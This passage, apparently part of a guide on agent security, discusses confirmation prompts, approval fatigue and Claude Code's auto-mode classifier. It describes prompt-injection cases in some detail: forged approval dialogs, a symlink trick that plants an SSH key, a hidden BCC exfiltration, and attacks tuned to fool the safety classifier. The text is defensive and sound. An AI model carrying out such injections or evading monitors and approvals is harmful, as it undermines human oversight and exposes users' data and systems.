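The software company's staff still issue refunds above $50 and check every reply that falls outside the fixed form. Each check takes time and helps only if the employee can tell a harmful action from a harmless one. The company therefore has to choose which actions need a *confirmation prompt*, a request that a person approve a specific action before it runs.

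Many products don't choose which actions need confirmation. *Reframing LLM Agent Security as an Agent-Human Interaction Problem* (2026) covers 15 systems that ask for approval while the agent runs, and most of them ask about every command or every outside call. Claude Code was one of these, but it has since made automatic review its default. OpenAI advises companies to ask for approval of consequential actions, such as changing production systems, moving sensitive data, and taking material financial or external actions.

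### Score each action

A team can sort the model's actions with four questions. The team should answer them for the worst arguments the software would accept, not for a typical request.

| Question | 0 points | 1 point | 2 points |
|---|---|---|---|
| Can the company undo it? | Yes, easily | For a limited time, or at a cost | No |
| How large could the effect be? | Within a loss the company has agreed to accept | Larger, but limited to one payment or message | A customer's whole account or service, or several customers |
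| Whom does it reach outside the company? | Nobody | The session's own customer | Anyone else |
| Did untrusted content enter the session first? | No | Yes | (not used) |

The software allows an action that scores up to 3 points, requires a person's confirmation for one that scores 4 or 5, and refuses one that scores 6 or 7. These cut-offs are a judgement, and another company might reasonably move them. Here are the scores for eight of the support assistant's actions, with points listed in the order of the questions.

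| Action | Points | Decision |
|---|---|---|
| Read this customer's invoices | 0 + 0 + 0 + 1 = 1 | Allow |
| Write a case note in fixed fields | 0 + 0 + 0 + 1 = 1 | Allow |
| Send an invoice copy to the registered address, from a session that never received the ticket | 2 + 0 + 1 + 0 = 3 | Allow |
| Refund up to $50 within the daily budget, held for a day | 1 + 0 + 1 + 1 = 3 | Allow |
| Cancel a subscription | 1 + 2 + 0 + 1 = 4 | Ask |
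| Send a free-text reply | 2 + 1 + 1 + 1 = 5 | Ask |
| Refund more than $50 | 2 + 1 + 1 + 1 = 5 | Ask |
| Change the registered email address | 2 + 2 + 2 + 1 = 7 | Forbid |

The last action would let an attacker take over the account, as happened with Meta's assistant on Instagram. Customers can still change their address themselves after logging in.

Enforced limits reduce the number of confirmation prompts. Without the one-day hold, small refunds would score 4 and an employee would have to approve each one. Invoice copies would also score 4 and need approval if the session that sent them had read the ticket.

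The total can understate the risk of an action that has one very bad answer. For example, deleting all of a customer's records scores 5 because it reaches nobody outside the company. A support assistant never needs to do this, and the company should forbid any action the job doesn't require, whatever its score.

Ordinary software has to determine whether an action needs confirmation, because a hijacked agent will give whatever answer avoids a confirmation request. Kodathala, Pollishetty and Cargill (2026), in *Approve What, Exactly?*, tested a policy that required no confirmation for memory writes a user had requested. The agent got its write through by claiming that a user had requested it.

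Another approach is to check where the values in an action came from. In *The Verifiable Action Card*, Irshad, Mughees and colleagues (2026) built a browser agent that asks for a single tap when the user named the recipient and amount, and displays a warning when they came from somewhere else. It compares domains as well as names, so a request to "email Sarah" doesn't cover `sarah@evil-exfil.com`. This suits a personal assistant, whose user is trusted, but would do little for the support desk, where the person naming the recipient may be the attacker.

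### What a useful prompt shows

According to OpenAI, ChatGPT has software that detects when information from a conversation is about to go to a third party. The software either shows the user the information and asks for confirmation, or blocks the transfer and tells the model to try another way. Users can judge such a prompt fairly easily because they know, for example, whether a hotel's website needs their travel dates or their home address.

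A coding agent might ask permission to run `python sync.py`. The confirmation prompt is accurate but nearly useless, because the user can't tell which files the script reads or where it sends them without opening the script.

A good prompt shows the effect of the action, the resource it changes, the recipient, and any data that will leave. Ordinary code should take all of this from the tool call and the company's own records. For a refund, the employee might see this:

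```text
REFUND $180.00 to Hartwell Ltd, card ending 4471
Invoice 10517: $180.00, paid once, on 3 September
Earlier refunds on this invoice: none
Text on customer's statement: "Invoice 10517"
```

Written by the assistant, not checked: "duplicate charge"
```

The assistant's reason is a duplicate charge, but the payment record shows that the customer paid only once. If the assistant had written the whole prompt, the employee would probably have seen only a plausible request.

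Kodathala and colleagues tested how much it matters where the text of a confirmation request comes from. In one case, a user asks an agent to email a report to their boss, and the hijacked agent adds a blind copy to an outside address. The researchers showed the request to 15 language models acting as approvers. All 15 approved it when they saw the agent's own description, which didn't mention the copy, but refused when they saw a prompt built from the tool call, with both recipients in its title.

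Across 23 attacks, the models caught 30% when they read the agent's descriptions and 98% when they read prompts built by code. They also refused 16% of harmless requests, mostly because the test messages contained placeholders such as `<report placeholder>`, which looked wrong. Without those refusals, the refusal rate would be about 2%. The study had no human approvers, so it didn't measure how often people would catch the same attacks.

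The agent's explanation may do harm even when the confirmation prompt also shows accurate facts. In simulations where the agent lied about what it was doing, 54% of attacks succeeded when the approver saw only the agent's description. When code built the prompt, the rate fell to 3% for a simulated approver that compared the prompt with the task, but stayed at 54% for one that believed the agent's explanation whenever the prompt included it. Removing the explanation cut the second approver's rate to 5%. Language models acting as approvers made nearly the same decisions without the explanation. Nobody has tested people, so it seems safest to leave the explanation out or hide it until the reviewer asks for it.

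Confirmation prompts can also be too short. With another simulated approver, a version that showed only the payee and amount let through 20% of attacks, compared with 6% for the full prompt. The short version left out the subject and body of emails, and any extra recipients.

### Forged dialogs

An attacker who can influence the text of a confirmation prompt can trick a person into approving an attack. The security company Checkmarx named this "Lies-in-the-Loop" in September 2025 (Security Boulevard, *Checkmarx Surfaces Lies-in-the-Middle Attack to Compromise AI Tools*, 2025). Hidden instructions make a coding agent propose a dangerous command surrounded by long, harmless-looking text. The text pushes the command off the screen, and a developer who scrolls to the top finds only more harmless text.

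Checkmarx's *Turning AI Safeguards Into Weapons with HITL Dialog Forging* adds that an attacker could influence the one-line summary that Claude Code attached to its confirmation prompt. If an app interprets the command as Markdown, the attacker could also close the box that displays the real command and open a second one containing something like `git status`. Checkmarx found that Microsoft's Copilot Chat interpreted Markdown in commands only after the user had answered, so the trick didn't work there.

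Anthropic classified Checkmarx's reports as outside its threat model. Microsoft said the behaviour wasn't a security vulnerability, partly because it required the user to take several non-default actions.

Several repairs work together:

- The software escapes formatting, makes invisible characters visible, and collapses long runs of blanks.
- It limits the length of the prompt and flags anything it has shortened.
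- It separates the program from its arguments, so an attacker can't bury a second command in a long string.
- It writes any summary from the finished call, after the agent can no longer change it.

The confirmation prompt also has to appear in a part of the screen the attacker can't draw on. In one of Irshad and colleagues' tests, a web page has a button labelled "Save draft" that actually transfers 5,000 to a stranger. A prompt based on the label would ask the user to approve saving a draft. The researchers' browser instead reads the form behind the button and displays the transfer in its own window frame, outside the page, with "Deny" as the default.

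They report that no attack succeeded with this design on any model they tested, while 78% of legitimate tasks finished. Attacks on the undefended browser succeeded 68% to 100% of the time according to their abstract, and 80% to 100% according to their introduction. The benchmark has only 24 scenarios, and a program stood in for the person.

### Prompts that name the wrong target

A confirmation prompt can mislead even if nobody forges it. Wiz's *GhostApproval* (July 2026) tested six coding assistants with a project containing a *symbolic link*, a file that redirects to another file. The link was named `project_settings.json` but led to the list of keys allowed to log in to the developer's computer. The project's instructions told the agent to add a line to the settings, and that line was the attacker's key.

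Claude Code showed the prompt "Make this edit to project_settings.json?" The prompt left out that the file was a link to something else, though this was already in Claude Code's reasoning. Windsurf and Amazon Q wrote the file before the user could answer, so their buttons could only undo the change. Augment showed no confirmation prompt.

Amazon, Cursor and Google fixed the problem. Anthropic first replied that the scenario was outside its threat model because the user had chosen to trust the folder and had then approved the edit. It later told Wiz that it had shipped a warning about such links on 5 February, nine days before the report. Wiz lists a later version in its results, so it is unclear why the warning didn't appear.

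The first reply isn't convincing, because someone who trusts a folder hasn't agreed to edits outside it, and a developer can't consent to a change that the prompt doesn't show. The fix also takes little work. The software follows every link before it displays the prompt, shows the real location, warns if that is outside the project, and writes nothing until the user agrees.

### Actions that change after approval

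An agent often pauses while a person decides whether to approve a call, and something may change the call before it runs. Kodathala and colleagues were able to test eight approval mechanisms in popular agent frameworks for this weakness. Three always ran the call that the person had approved. One failed only if an attacker could write to its database. The other four, including those in LangGraph and Pydantic AI, let the call be changed by whoever resumed the run, whoever supplied its history, or other code in the framework.

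European payment rules tie the code a customer enters for a remote payment to the amount and payee they saw, and changing either one cancels the code. A person's confirmation of an agent's action needs to be tied to every argument in the same way, because a changed attachment can matter as much as a changed amount.

Kodathala and colleagues do it with a *fingerprint*, a short value that a standard function (SHA-256) computes from a longer text. Changing one digit of the text gives a completely different fingerprint, and nobody knows how to find two texts that share one. The approval then works like this:

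1. A gateway outside the agent writes the tool call in a standard form, with every argument in a fixed order, and computes its fingerprint.
2. The gateway stores the call and builds the prompt from the stored copy.
3. The user approves on their phone, which signs the fingerprint together with a number that is unique to this approval.
4. The gateway marks the approval as used and runs the stored call. If the agent sends the call again with different arguments, the fingerprints don't match and the gateway refuses.

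In scripted tests, an attacker could swap the arguments every time if the approval wasn't tied to them, and the fingerprint blocked every swap. *Agent-First Tool API* (2026) describes a simpler version that saves the whole call and resumes from the saved copy.

A fingerprint can detect changes to the call, but not changes in the circumstances that made it appropriate. While the employee reads the refund prompt, a colleague may refund the same invoice by phone. Running the unchanged call would then pay the customer twice. The payment system therefore has to check the invoice again just before it pays, and approvals should expire quickly. Web pages can also rewrite a form at the moment of submission, so Irshad and colleagues' browser compares the outgoing recipient and amount with the approved ones.

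### Approvals that cover later actions

In five of the frameworks that Kodathala and colleagues audited, someone who restored an earlier saved state of a run could use the same approval twice. Developers can prevent this by giving each approval a unique number and keeping a record of used approvals outside the run.

People also grant broader permission on purpose. Many Claude Desktop users chose "Always allow" and stopped seeing the prompts that might have exposed the GitHub attack. A safer grant fixes all but a few fields and limits what can go in those. For example, an employee could let the assistant send up to three more replies, with any wording, to the same customer in the same session. Kodathala and colleagues' grants always fix any recipient, account, file path or web address, limit the number of uses, and expire.

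Even narrow grants help some reviewers and hurt others. When an attacker tried to extend an approval to a new recipient, grants cut the attacker's success rate from 20% to zero against a simulated approver who read the main fields but sometimes missed a difference. Against one who often approved without reading, grants raised the rate from 30% to 70%, because one careless click also approved the later actions. OpenAI prefers time-limited grants to permanent ones and advises companies to review the task again after each approved exception.

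### Harmful plans in small steps

The company requires a person to confirm refunds above $50, so an attacker who wants $180 can avoid confirmation by requesting four refunds of $45. In Kodathala and colleagues' tests, this kind of splitting always worked when the software considered each payment separately, but never when it also counted totals. Their default setting requires a new confirmation after five actions or $200 within ten minutes, and earlier approvals cannot satisfy this requirement.

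The support assistant's daily budget wouldn't catch four $45 refunds, but a per-customer limit could require an employee to confirm a customer's second refund in a month.

Running totals don't help when a leak involves different kinds of steps. An agent might read a contract, save part of it under an ordinary file name, and attach the file to a message. A reviewer who sees only "attach notes.txt" has no reason to object. The software should record that the session has read a contract, then show this and the file's contents whenever it asks a person to confirm sending something out.

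If an agent writes a program that calls several tools, the software can inspect the program before it runs. *Governance by Construction for Generalist Agents* (2026) describes a system that scans the generated code for sensitive tools and pauses until someone approves. The reviewer can then see the steps together. But the recipients may be set only while the program runs, so the gateway still has to check each call when it arrives.

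### Reviewers who can't judge

Some confirmation prompts are honest and complete, but the person reading them doesn't know the answer. A developer asked to approve installing an unfamiliar package usually can't tell from its name whether it is malicious. A support employee may not know whether a contract allows cancellation mid-term.

The software can often supply the missing fact, such as the contract's notice period. It can also let the reviewer edit a proposed call, as LangChain does, instead of only approving or rejecting it. An edited call needs a new fingerprint because it is no longer the call the agent proposed.

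If no available reviewer could tell a good request from a bad one, asking for confirmation only shifts the blame to whoever approves the request. The company should instead forbid the action or limit the harm it could do, such as by installing a package in a sandbox.

### Who should approve

The user is usually the best judge of what they asked for, so a traveller should confirm their own booking. User confirmation works less well when the action affects someone else's property, or when the user may be the attacker, since a customer who falsely claims a refund would also confirm it.

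A second person can catch the mistake when an attacker has deceived the user, and can stop a user who is dishonest. The owner of the affected system is more likely to know what else depends on it. For the invoice agent, an accounts clerk might see that a subscription renewal is affordable, but someone with authority to sign contracts should decide whether to renew.

The agent must not choose who approves an action, or find that person through a channel others can use. Kodathala and colleagues recount three failures from *Agents of Chaos*. One agent asked twice for confirmation before a destructive reset, and both answers came from the outsider who had requested it. Another accepted an outsider as its owner because they had copied the owner's display name. In the third case, two agents rightly distrusted a deceptive email, but then tried to verify their owner through the owner's chat account,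 which might itself have been compromised.

*Agent-First Tool API* avoids this by naming the approver in each tool's policy. The agent can do other work while it waits, and it receives the approver's reason if the request is refused. The support assistant, however, should be told only that the request was refused, because it might pass the reason on to the customer. An attacker who learns that staff refused a refund because there was no second payment would know to fake evidence of one next time.

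Asking for confirmation on a separate phone may be unnecessary. In Kodathala and colleagues' tests, a trusted prompt on the agent's own computer stopped almost exactly the same attacks as a phone prompt. However, none of the tests let the attacker control that computer's display. A coding agent with a shell on the approver's laptop might be able to control it, so a phone makes more sense for that agent than for a support desk whose approval page runs on a separate server.

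Ordinary support staff can approve the support assistant's free-text replies. Employees who can open the payment records approve refunds above $50, and a second person in finance also approves very large ones. The customer's registered account owner logs in to confirm a cancellation, because the person who wrote the ticket may be a junior employee without the authority to cancel.

### Confirming a send doesn't undo a disclosure

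A confirmation prompt controls only the action it describes. Suppose a customer forwards a log file containing a hidden instruction, and the assistant follows it by reading the customer's contracts and copying their terms into a draft. The employee notices and rejects the draft. But the assistant has already used those terms in a search, and under the company's first design, the search log would have sent them to an outside supplier.

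The contract terms also remain in the session's context after the rejection. The assistant could reword them in its next draft or put them in any other field it can write to. Rejecting a suspicious draft should therefore end the session and discard its context, and staff should check what the assistant had already searched for and written.

For this reason, OpenAI advises limiting both what an agent can read and what it can send. When reading is the sensitive step, the assistant should ask for confirmation before it reads. Most support tickets can be resolved without the contract, so the company could keep contracts closed by default and have the assistant ask an employee to open one. The employee can compare that request with the ticket before any of the contract enters the model's context.

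## Approval fatigue and what can replace routine prompts

A confirmation prompt that shows the right facts still protects nobody if the person approves it without reading it. *Approval fatigue* is the decline in attention that comes from approving many routine prompts. Under the split design, the software company's staff check 150 drafts a day. A developer who approves a coding agent's commands one by one may answer hundreds of prompts a day.

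### Habituation to browser warnings

Psychologists call a weakening response to a repeated stimulus *habituation*. Security researchers studied it in browser warnings long before AI agents existed. A review of that research, *Harnessing the Challenges and Solutions to Improve Security Warnings*, describes an experiment in which the time people spent on a repeated message fell from about 15 seconds to 2 within three exposures.

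But people didn't ignore every warning. *Alice in Warningland* (Akhawe and Felt, 2013) recorded how Firefox and Chrome users responded to more than 25 million warnings during ordinary browsing. Users clicked through 9% to 23% of the warnings about malware and fake login pages. They clicked through 70.2% of Chrome's warnings that it couldn't verify a site's identity, compared with 33.0% of Firefox's. Firefox required three clicks and by default remembered the user's decision, while Chrome required one click and asked again on every visit. Both differences may have contributed to the gap, and Akhawe and Felt found that users paid less attention to warnings they saw often.

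Habituation can also carry over to a prompt the person has never seen. For *The Fog of Warnings* (2019), Vance, Eargle and colleagues had 600 people sort pictures of Batman online. Some saw a security warning after the first picture. Others first had to dismiss 14 routine messages about their score, and they paid less attention to the warning and heeded it less often. The effect depended on how closely the warning resembled the messages. To check whether people were simply tired, the researchers showed some participants a yellow duck instead of a warning, and concluded that they weren't. A prompt about a large refund should therefore look quite different from the screen where staff approve ordinary drafts.

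### The study of 1,053 testers

Anthropic reported a similar experiment with a coding agent in August 2026, when it announced that auto mode would become Claude Code's default. A research vendor recruited 1,053 paid professional testers for a coding study. The testers knew they were being evaluated, but not what behaviour the study measured. Partway through each session, one permission prompt showed a clearly dangerous command in place of the real one. Approving it did no harm because only the displayed text had changed.

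The testers refused the dangerous command 143 times (13.6%). Auto mode's classifier blocked 937 of the same commands (89%). Anthropic also reports that the classifier blocked 800 commands that a tester approved, and testers refused 6 that the classifier allowed. The other figures in the table are calculated from these by subtraction.

| | Classifier blocked | Classifier allowed | Total |
|---|---|---|---|
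| Tester refused | 137 | 6 | 143 |
| Tester approved | 800 | 110 | 910 |
| Total | 937 | 116 | 1,053 |

Using both reviewers would have stopped 943 commands instead of the classifier's 937, or 89.6% instead of 89.0%. If the testers had caught the classifier's misses at the same rate as other dangerous commands, they would have caught about 16 of the 116. They caught 6, so the commands that got past the classifier were probably harder for people to spot too. Willison points out that the classifier still let 11% through, but on these figures a routine human check would have caught few of those commands.

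Testers refused about 17% of dangerous commands early in a session and about 5% after 50 or more prompts, while the classifier's refusal rate stayed flat. Even early on, testers approved about 83% of these commands, so approval fatigue explains only a small part of the failure. Showing people fewer prompts should help, but they also need prompts that make the danger visible and enough knowledge to recognise it.

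The study is seriously limited because Anthropic was testing its own product and the testers worked on an artificial project where they had nothing to lose. Earlier laboratory studies suggest that people ignore more warnings under such conditions. Akhawe and Felt describe one from 2007 in which 53% of participants clicked through a warning on a bank's website, but only 36% of those using their own passwords did. In another, more than 40% of participants said the laboratory setting had influenced them to click through. Developers protecting their own production database would probably refuse more than 13.6% of dangerous commands, though they would have to refuse far more to match the classifier.

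The study also measured only how many dangerous commands each reviewer caught, so a reviewer who refused everything would score 100% despite being useless. Anthropic doesn't report how many harmless commands the classifier would have blocked in these sessions, although it measured this separately when it launched auto mode.

### What approval rates can show

In ordinary use, people approve 97% of Claude Code's permission prompts. The figure was 93% in March 2026, according to Anthropic's *How we built Claude Code auto mode* (2026). Anthropic takes the high rate as a sign that many users click through by reflex, though it accepts that most of the commands are probably safe.

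A high approval rate doesn't prove inattention. Suppose one prompt in 1,000 is harmful. A perfect reviewer would approve 99.9% of prompts and stop every harmful one, while someone who never read any would approve 100% and stop none. The tester study is better evidence than the approval rate because it shows how people respond to harmful prompts. Akhawe and Felt similarly point out that someone who clicks through a browser warning may have ignored it or may have correctly judged it to be a false alarm.

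Anthropic compares how often users reject permission prompts (3%) with how often they reject Claude's plans for a task (39%). The higher rate suggests that people read plans, but the two rates aren't a fair comparison of how carefully people check for danger. The button for rejecting a plan is labelled "No, keep planning", and users press it to tell Claude what to change, so many of those rejections may be about the quality of the work.

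People seem to want fewer prompts. A quarter of interactive sessions start with permission checks bypassed, and 62% of users have used that mode or clicked "don't ask again" for shell commands.

Anthropic also looked for harm in real sessions from May and June 2026 that its safety systems had flagged, using accounts that had agreed to this use of their data. A model graded each session on how severe the harm was and how explicitly the user had asked for the action. Serious harm that the user hadn't explicitly asked for, such as deleting rows from a production database, appeared in 6.3% of the sessions with manual approval and 2.4% of those in auto mode.

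This agrees with the tester study, but it is weaker evidence because nobody assigned users to a mode. Developers may have kept manual approval for their riskiest work, which would make it look worse than it is. The percentages are also shares of flagged sessions, so the comparison across all sessions could be quite different if the safety systems flagged sessions in one mode more often.

### Approve a plan instead of each step

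One alternative is to ask a person to approve the whole task at once. In Claude Code's plan mode, the agent reads files and runs commands to explore the project, then presents a plan. It normally can't edit the source code until the user approves the plan. The user can rewrite the plan before approving it, which is a much better use of their attention than judging 50 commands out of context.

However, the agent writes the plan and can leave out a harmful step, just as it can when describing a single action. Approving the plan also ends plan mode, after which the session's permission mode determines which actions run. If the agent later opens a hostile file, it may do something that was never in the plan, so its actions still need to be checked.

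People may also be too easily persuaded by a plan they have read. Mediafax's *Agenții AI pot influența judecata experților* reports on an experiment, published by Anthropic in October 2026, in which 50 experienced analysts used Claude Code to evaluate a fictional advice programme for farms. The analysts made four decisions about method, and for each one the researchers had secretly told the agent to favour one of two reasonable options, chosen at random, and to argue for it without distorting the data. The analysts chose the favoured option 86% of the time, compared with the roughly 50% expected if the agent had no influence.

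Analysts switched from a preference they had already stated 60% of the time when the agent argued against it, and 6% of the time when the agent agreed with it. Both options were defensible, so the experiment doesn't show that analysts would accept a harmful plan. But 52% of those who answered the final questionnaire thought the recommendation reflected their own judgement more than the agent's, so a reviewer may not notice how much the agent has influenced them.

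### Sandboxes and standing rules

An action doesn't need approval if a sandbox already prevents it from doing damage. Anthropic describes sandboxing as safe but laborious to maintain, because someone has to configure each new capability, and anything that needs the network or the host machine breaks the isolation.

A coding agent confined to its workspace can still delete the source code it is supposed to edit. Wu, Chen and colleagues (2026) note in *Shall We Approve?* that OpenAI's Codex, in its default sandbox, sends its automatic reviewer only the requests that leave the workspace. Most of the harmful actions in their tests would not have reached that reviewer. A team that drops approval prompts inside a sandbox therefore needs a copy of the work somewhere the agent can't write.

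Standing rules let a person make a decision once. In Claude Code, an allow rule can let the agent run `npm test` without asking, an ask rule can require a prompt before every `git push`, and a deny rule can block a command. Deny rules apply even when the user has bypassed the other permission checks.

A deny rule is also more reliable than an instruction in the conversation. If the user writes "don't push", auto mode's classifier treats this as a reason to block pushes. But Claude Code shortens long conversations to fit the model's context, and Anthropic warns that this can remove the message, leaving the classifier with no record of it. A deny rule is stored separately, so it still applies.

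The main problem with allow rules is that people make them too broad. In June 2026, 49.5% of active command-line users had written at least one allow rule for shell commands, and that share was growing by about one percentage point a week. Many of these rules allow any command that starts with `python` or `node`, which permits almost anything because a script can do whatever the user's account can do. Auto mode ignores such rules while it is on, though Anthropic says its list of them can't be complete.

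Deny and ask rules match the text of a command, so they can be too narrow. A rule about `git push` may not catch a script that pushes the code another way. If nobody should be able to push to the main branch without review, the service that hosts the code should enforce that.

### How auto mode decides

Auto mode combines standing rules with its classifier, which is a second language model. With a few exceptions, Claude Code handles each action in this order:

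1. It applies the user's allow, ask and deny rules, leaving out the allow rules that are too broad.
2. It allows the agent to read files and to edit those inside the project, apart from certain protected files. The first time the agent's file tools read something outside the project, the user gets a prompt.
3. It sends everything else to the classifier, including most shell commands, web requests and calls to outside tools.
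4. If the classifier blocks the action, the agent receives a reason and can look for a safer way to do the job.
5. After three blocks in a row, or 20 in a session, Claude Code returns to manual approval. If the user approves the next action, auto mode resumes.

When the agent runs unattended, there is nobody to ask at the last step. The blocked action doesn't run, but the agent keeps working on the rest of the task.

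Anthropic's article from March describes a two-stage classifier. The first stage gives a quick yes or no and leans towards blocking. The second reasons more carefully, but only about actions the first flagged. On 10,000 real tool calls by Anthropic's employees, the first stage alone would have blocked 8.5% of harmless actions, and the two together blocked 0.4%. Adding the second stage also let more dangerous actions through, raising the share missed from 6.6% to 17% on 52 real cases where an agent had gone beyond what its user wanted.

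The classifier receives the user's messages, the project's standing instructions and most of the agent's tool calls. It doesn't receive the agent's explanations, because a hijacked agent could use them to argue that a dangerous action was safe. It also doesn't receive the text that tools return, where most injections arrive. Anthropic found that including both made the classifier worse at catching agents that exceeded their instructions. A separate program scans tool results and adds a warning to the agent's context when something looks like an injection. No attack succeeded in the Trajectory Labs test, which covered this whole arrangement, not only the classifier.

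### What counts as permission

In most of the misses that Anthropic examined in March, the classifier had identified the danger but misclassified the action as one the user had agreed to. For example, a user who says "clean up the PR" wants a tidier code change and hasn't agreed to a force push, which can overwrite the project's shared history. Anthropic reported that it had tried to fix this by rewording the classifier's instructions, but had found no wording whose benefits outweighed its drawbacks.

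Its current documentation requires a user giving such permission to name both the action and the detail that makes it dangerous, such as the branch a force push would overwrite. Saying "you can force-push" isn't enough, and permission normally covers only one action.

This standard still depends on the user's messages coming from the user. *Ajar* (2026), which measures how much access various agent defences leave open, found that auto mode allowed every tested call when the instruction to make it was in the user's message. That is reasonable when a developer is typing. But if an application pastes a ticket into the user's message, a classifier that works this way could treat an attacker's text in the ticket as the user's consent. A company that builds its own reviewer should pass outside text to the reviewer separately or leave that text out.

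### Attacks designed to fool the classifier

A classifier is a language model, so an attacker may be able to fool it. Anthropic hired Apollo Research, a British AI safety company, to look for such failures in a two-week pilot. Apollo inserted synthetic attacks into records of real coding sessions. Some attacks involved data theft, and others involved broader failures and threats to safety.

Anthropic then gave the classifier more information, such as whether a code repository is public and whether a command would destroy unsaved work. Apollo retested it on attacks Anthropic had never seen. The classifier caught about half of the attacks it had previously missed, and missed about 2% of those it had previously caught. Across all the attacks, including those Apollo had shared with Anthropic, the miss rate fell from 12% to 7%.

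The rate on unseen attacks may have been slightly higher. If it also started at 12%, the two changes would bring it to about 8% ($0.12 \times 0.5 + 0.88 \times 0.02 \approx 0.078$). Anthropic warns against treating 7% as the miss rate in real use, because Apollo designed the attacks to find the classifier's weak points. An agent's ordinary mistakes should be easier to catch. A determined attacker who could practise against the classifier might do better than Apollo did in two weeks.

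### Harm hidden inside a script

Wu and colleagues, at Singapore Management University, tested a weakness that better judgement alone can't fix. Suppose an agent proposes `make clean && make`, a common command that removes old build files and rebuilds a program. What it deletes depends on a project file called a Makefile. In one project the command removes only temporary files, and in another it deletes the source code and its history, so a reviewer who reads only the command can't tell which will happen.

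One evaluation used 102 tasks in which a harmless-sounding request runs a tool that also deletes or overwrites a file it should leave alone. Each task had a safe twin with the same request and command but a harmless tool. Without any approval step, 71.6% of the dangerous tasks ended in harm, compared with 62.7% with auto mode. On a broader set of 682 tasks, auto mode reduced the rate of harm from 19.7% to 14.8%.

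These figures probably don't show how well auto mode performs as Anthropic ships it. Wu and colleagues ran the official Claude Code, but used an open Chinese model, GLM-5.3-Flash, as the agent and an OpenAI model as the classifier. The underlying gap remains with Anthropic's own models, however. Anthropic tells its classifier to judge the contents of any script the agent has written during the session, but the classifier doesn't see the contents of a script that was already in the project, because it doesn't receive the files the agent reads. Willison's malicious package exploits much the same gap, since the harm is in code that neither the agent nor the classifier has examined.

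Wu and colleagues propose running the command before deciding whether to allow it. Their system, Caper, takes a snapshot of the sandbox, runs the command without network access, and records its effects. A language model then compares a short report of those effects with the user's request. If the model approves, the changes stay. Otherwise, the software restores the snapshot and sends the agent the reason.

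When Caper replaced the classifier inside Claude Code, using the same two models, harm fell from 62.7% to 6.9% on the hidden-tool tasks and from 14.8% to 10.0% on the broader set. In a separate setup outside Claude Code, the report of effects reduced false alarms. Caper's reviewer blocked 61.8% of the safe twins without the report and 1.0% with it. A prompt that lists the files a script has just changed might help human reviewers in the same way, though the study didn't include any.

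The method only works for effects the software can undo, so Caper blocks outside connections during the trial run and records the attempts. An attacker could also write a script that detects the sandbox or waits until later to do harm. Wu and colleagues didn't test attackers who adapt in these ways.

### Wider use since August

Anthropic launched auto mode as a research preview in March 2026, when *Auto mode for Claude Code* still recommended using it in isolated environments. On 14 August, auto mode became the default for new Claude Code sessions on several subscription plans. On 22 October, Anthropic announced that from the following week auto mode would also be the default for new sessions in most Claude apps on the Pro, Max and Team plans. Enterprise administrators would get an email before the change reached their organisations.

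Recent versions of Claude Code start interactive terminal sessions in auto mode on every plan. *Claude Code Complete User Handbook* (2026) confirms this for the version it checked on 12 November. Sessions still start in manual mode for organisations that use Anthropic's configuration for HIPAA, the American law on health data. Unattended runs also start in manual mode, and Claude Code then denies any action that needs approval unless the developer has arranged another way to approve it.

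A team that relied on the old default should therefore check which mode its sessions now start in. Administrators can set a different default or turn auto mode off for the whole organisation.

### Save people for high-stakes changes

Anthropic doesn't claim that auto mode can replace a careful reviewer. It states in its documentation that the mode "does not guarantee safety". In March it wrote that switching to auto mode is "arguably a regression" for someone who already checks every action carefully.

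Anthropic advises people to review high-stakes changes themselves, although people did much worse than the classifier in its tester study. Those testers were answering routine prompts about a project that wasn't theirs. An engineer who is responsible for a database, and gets one prompt a week about deleting part of it, knows more and has a stronger reason to read carefully. This engineer could plausibly do far better than the testers' 13.6%, but Anthropic's study didn't test that.

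With Claude Code's ask rules, a team can let the classifier handle routine commands but require a person's approval before every production deployment. The team can also list actions that the classifier must never approve, even if a user asks for them. The database should still have a deletion delay and separate backups, because the classifier and the engineer can both be wrong about the same command.

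### Routine checks at the support desk

The software company can't simply copy auto mode for its support assistant. The evidence for auto mode comes from coding, where the user is usually trusted, while the support assistant's requests come from outsiders. A classifier could still screen the 150 daily drafts for problems such as promises of money. The classifier should be able to block a draft but not send one, at least until the company has tested it on its own tickets.

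If one employee checks all 150 drafts, most of them come after the point where the testers did worst. Five employees would check 30 each. Reading a draft for two minutes is different from glancing at a command, so the employees' attention may not decline in the same way, but sharing the work takes little extra effort.

Refunds above $50 should appear on a separate screen with a different layout, so that staff are less likely to carry over the habit of approving drafts. The company could also use the vendor's method of occasionally inserting a fake draft that the software will never send. If staff approve most of the fakes, the company can't count on their review and has to tighten the enforced limits instead.

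## Measure what the restrictions cost in usefulness

Every limit on the support assistant also affects genuine customers. Some wait longer for a reply, and others get no answer because the software blocked a harmless step. If the company counts only attacks, it will miss these delays and failures and may keep a restriction that protects very little.

An agent that does nothing has an attack success rate of zero. *Twin Agent* tested a design in which one model read bug reports, another could change the code, and nothing could pass from the first to the second. No attack succeeded, and the agent fixed none of the 232 bugs. Without the separation, the agent fixed 61.2% of them, but 97.0% of the attacks succeeded.

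A low attack success rate can also come from runs that end early. *INFUSE* (Nguyen, Guo and colleagues, 2026) tested 19 models on long command-line tasks. Claude Sonnet 4.6 had the lowest rate, 3.2%, but the researchers warn against reading this as robustness, because a spending cap had cut its runs short.

### Five measures

*Utility* is the share of legitimate tasks that an agent completes. A team should measure it without attacks, then again with hostile text in the material the agent reads. Three other measures cover drawbacks of the restrictions that may not show up in the completion rate.

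| Measure | What the software company would count |
|---|---|
| Utility without attack | Ordinary tickets that the assistant resolves correctly |
| Utility under attack | Tickets it resolves correctly although they contain an injection |
| Wrongly blocked actions | Harmless tool calls that the software refuses, as a share of all harmless calls |
| Added time | Staff minutes per day, and how much longer customers wait |
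| Tasks no longer offered | Requests the design rules out, such as searching other customers' tickets for the same fault |

The last of these is easy to overlook, because a team that removes a feature usually removes its test cases too. The dropped tasks should stay in the total. If an assistant completes 90% of the tasks it still offers, but a new design has dropped a fifth of the original ones, it completes only $0.9 \times 0.8 = 72\%$ of the original work.

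Teams should interpret utility under attack carefully because an attack can spoil the user's task even when it fails. In *INFUSE*, Claude Haiku 4.5 followed the attacker in only 8.4% of attacked runs, but it completed the user's task in 52.6% of them, compared with 75.0% of runs without attacks. GPT-5 completed the user's task in 94.3% of attacked runs and followed the attacker in 26.3%, so it must have done both in at least 20.6%. Those users would have received finished work and had little reason to suspect an attack. Teams should therefore also report how often the agent completes the task and the attack fails in the same run.

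A wrongly blocked action doesn't always make the task fail, since an agent that receives an explanation can often find another way. The delay from restrictions also varies widely. The automatic check in *Bounded Agents* took at most 0.24 milliseconds in 99% of cases. A confirmation prompt that arrives at 6 p.m. may go unanswered until 9 the next morning, even if the employee needs only 30 seconds to answer it.

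### Two very different results for Progent

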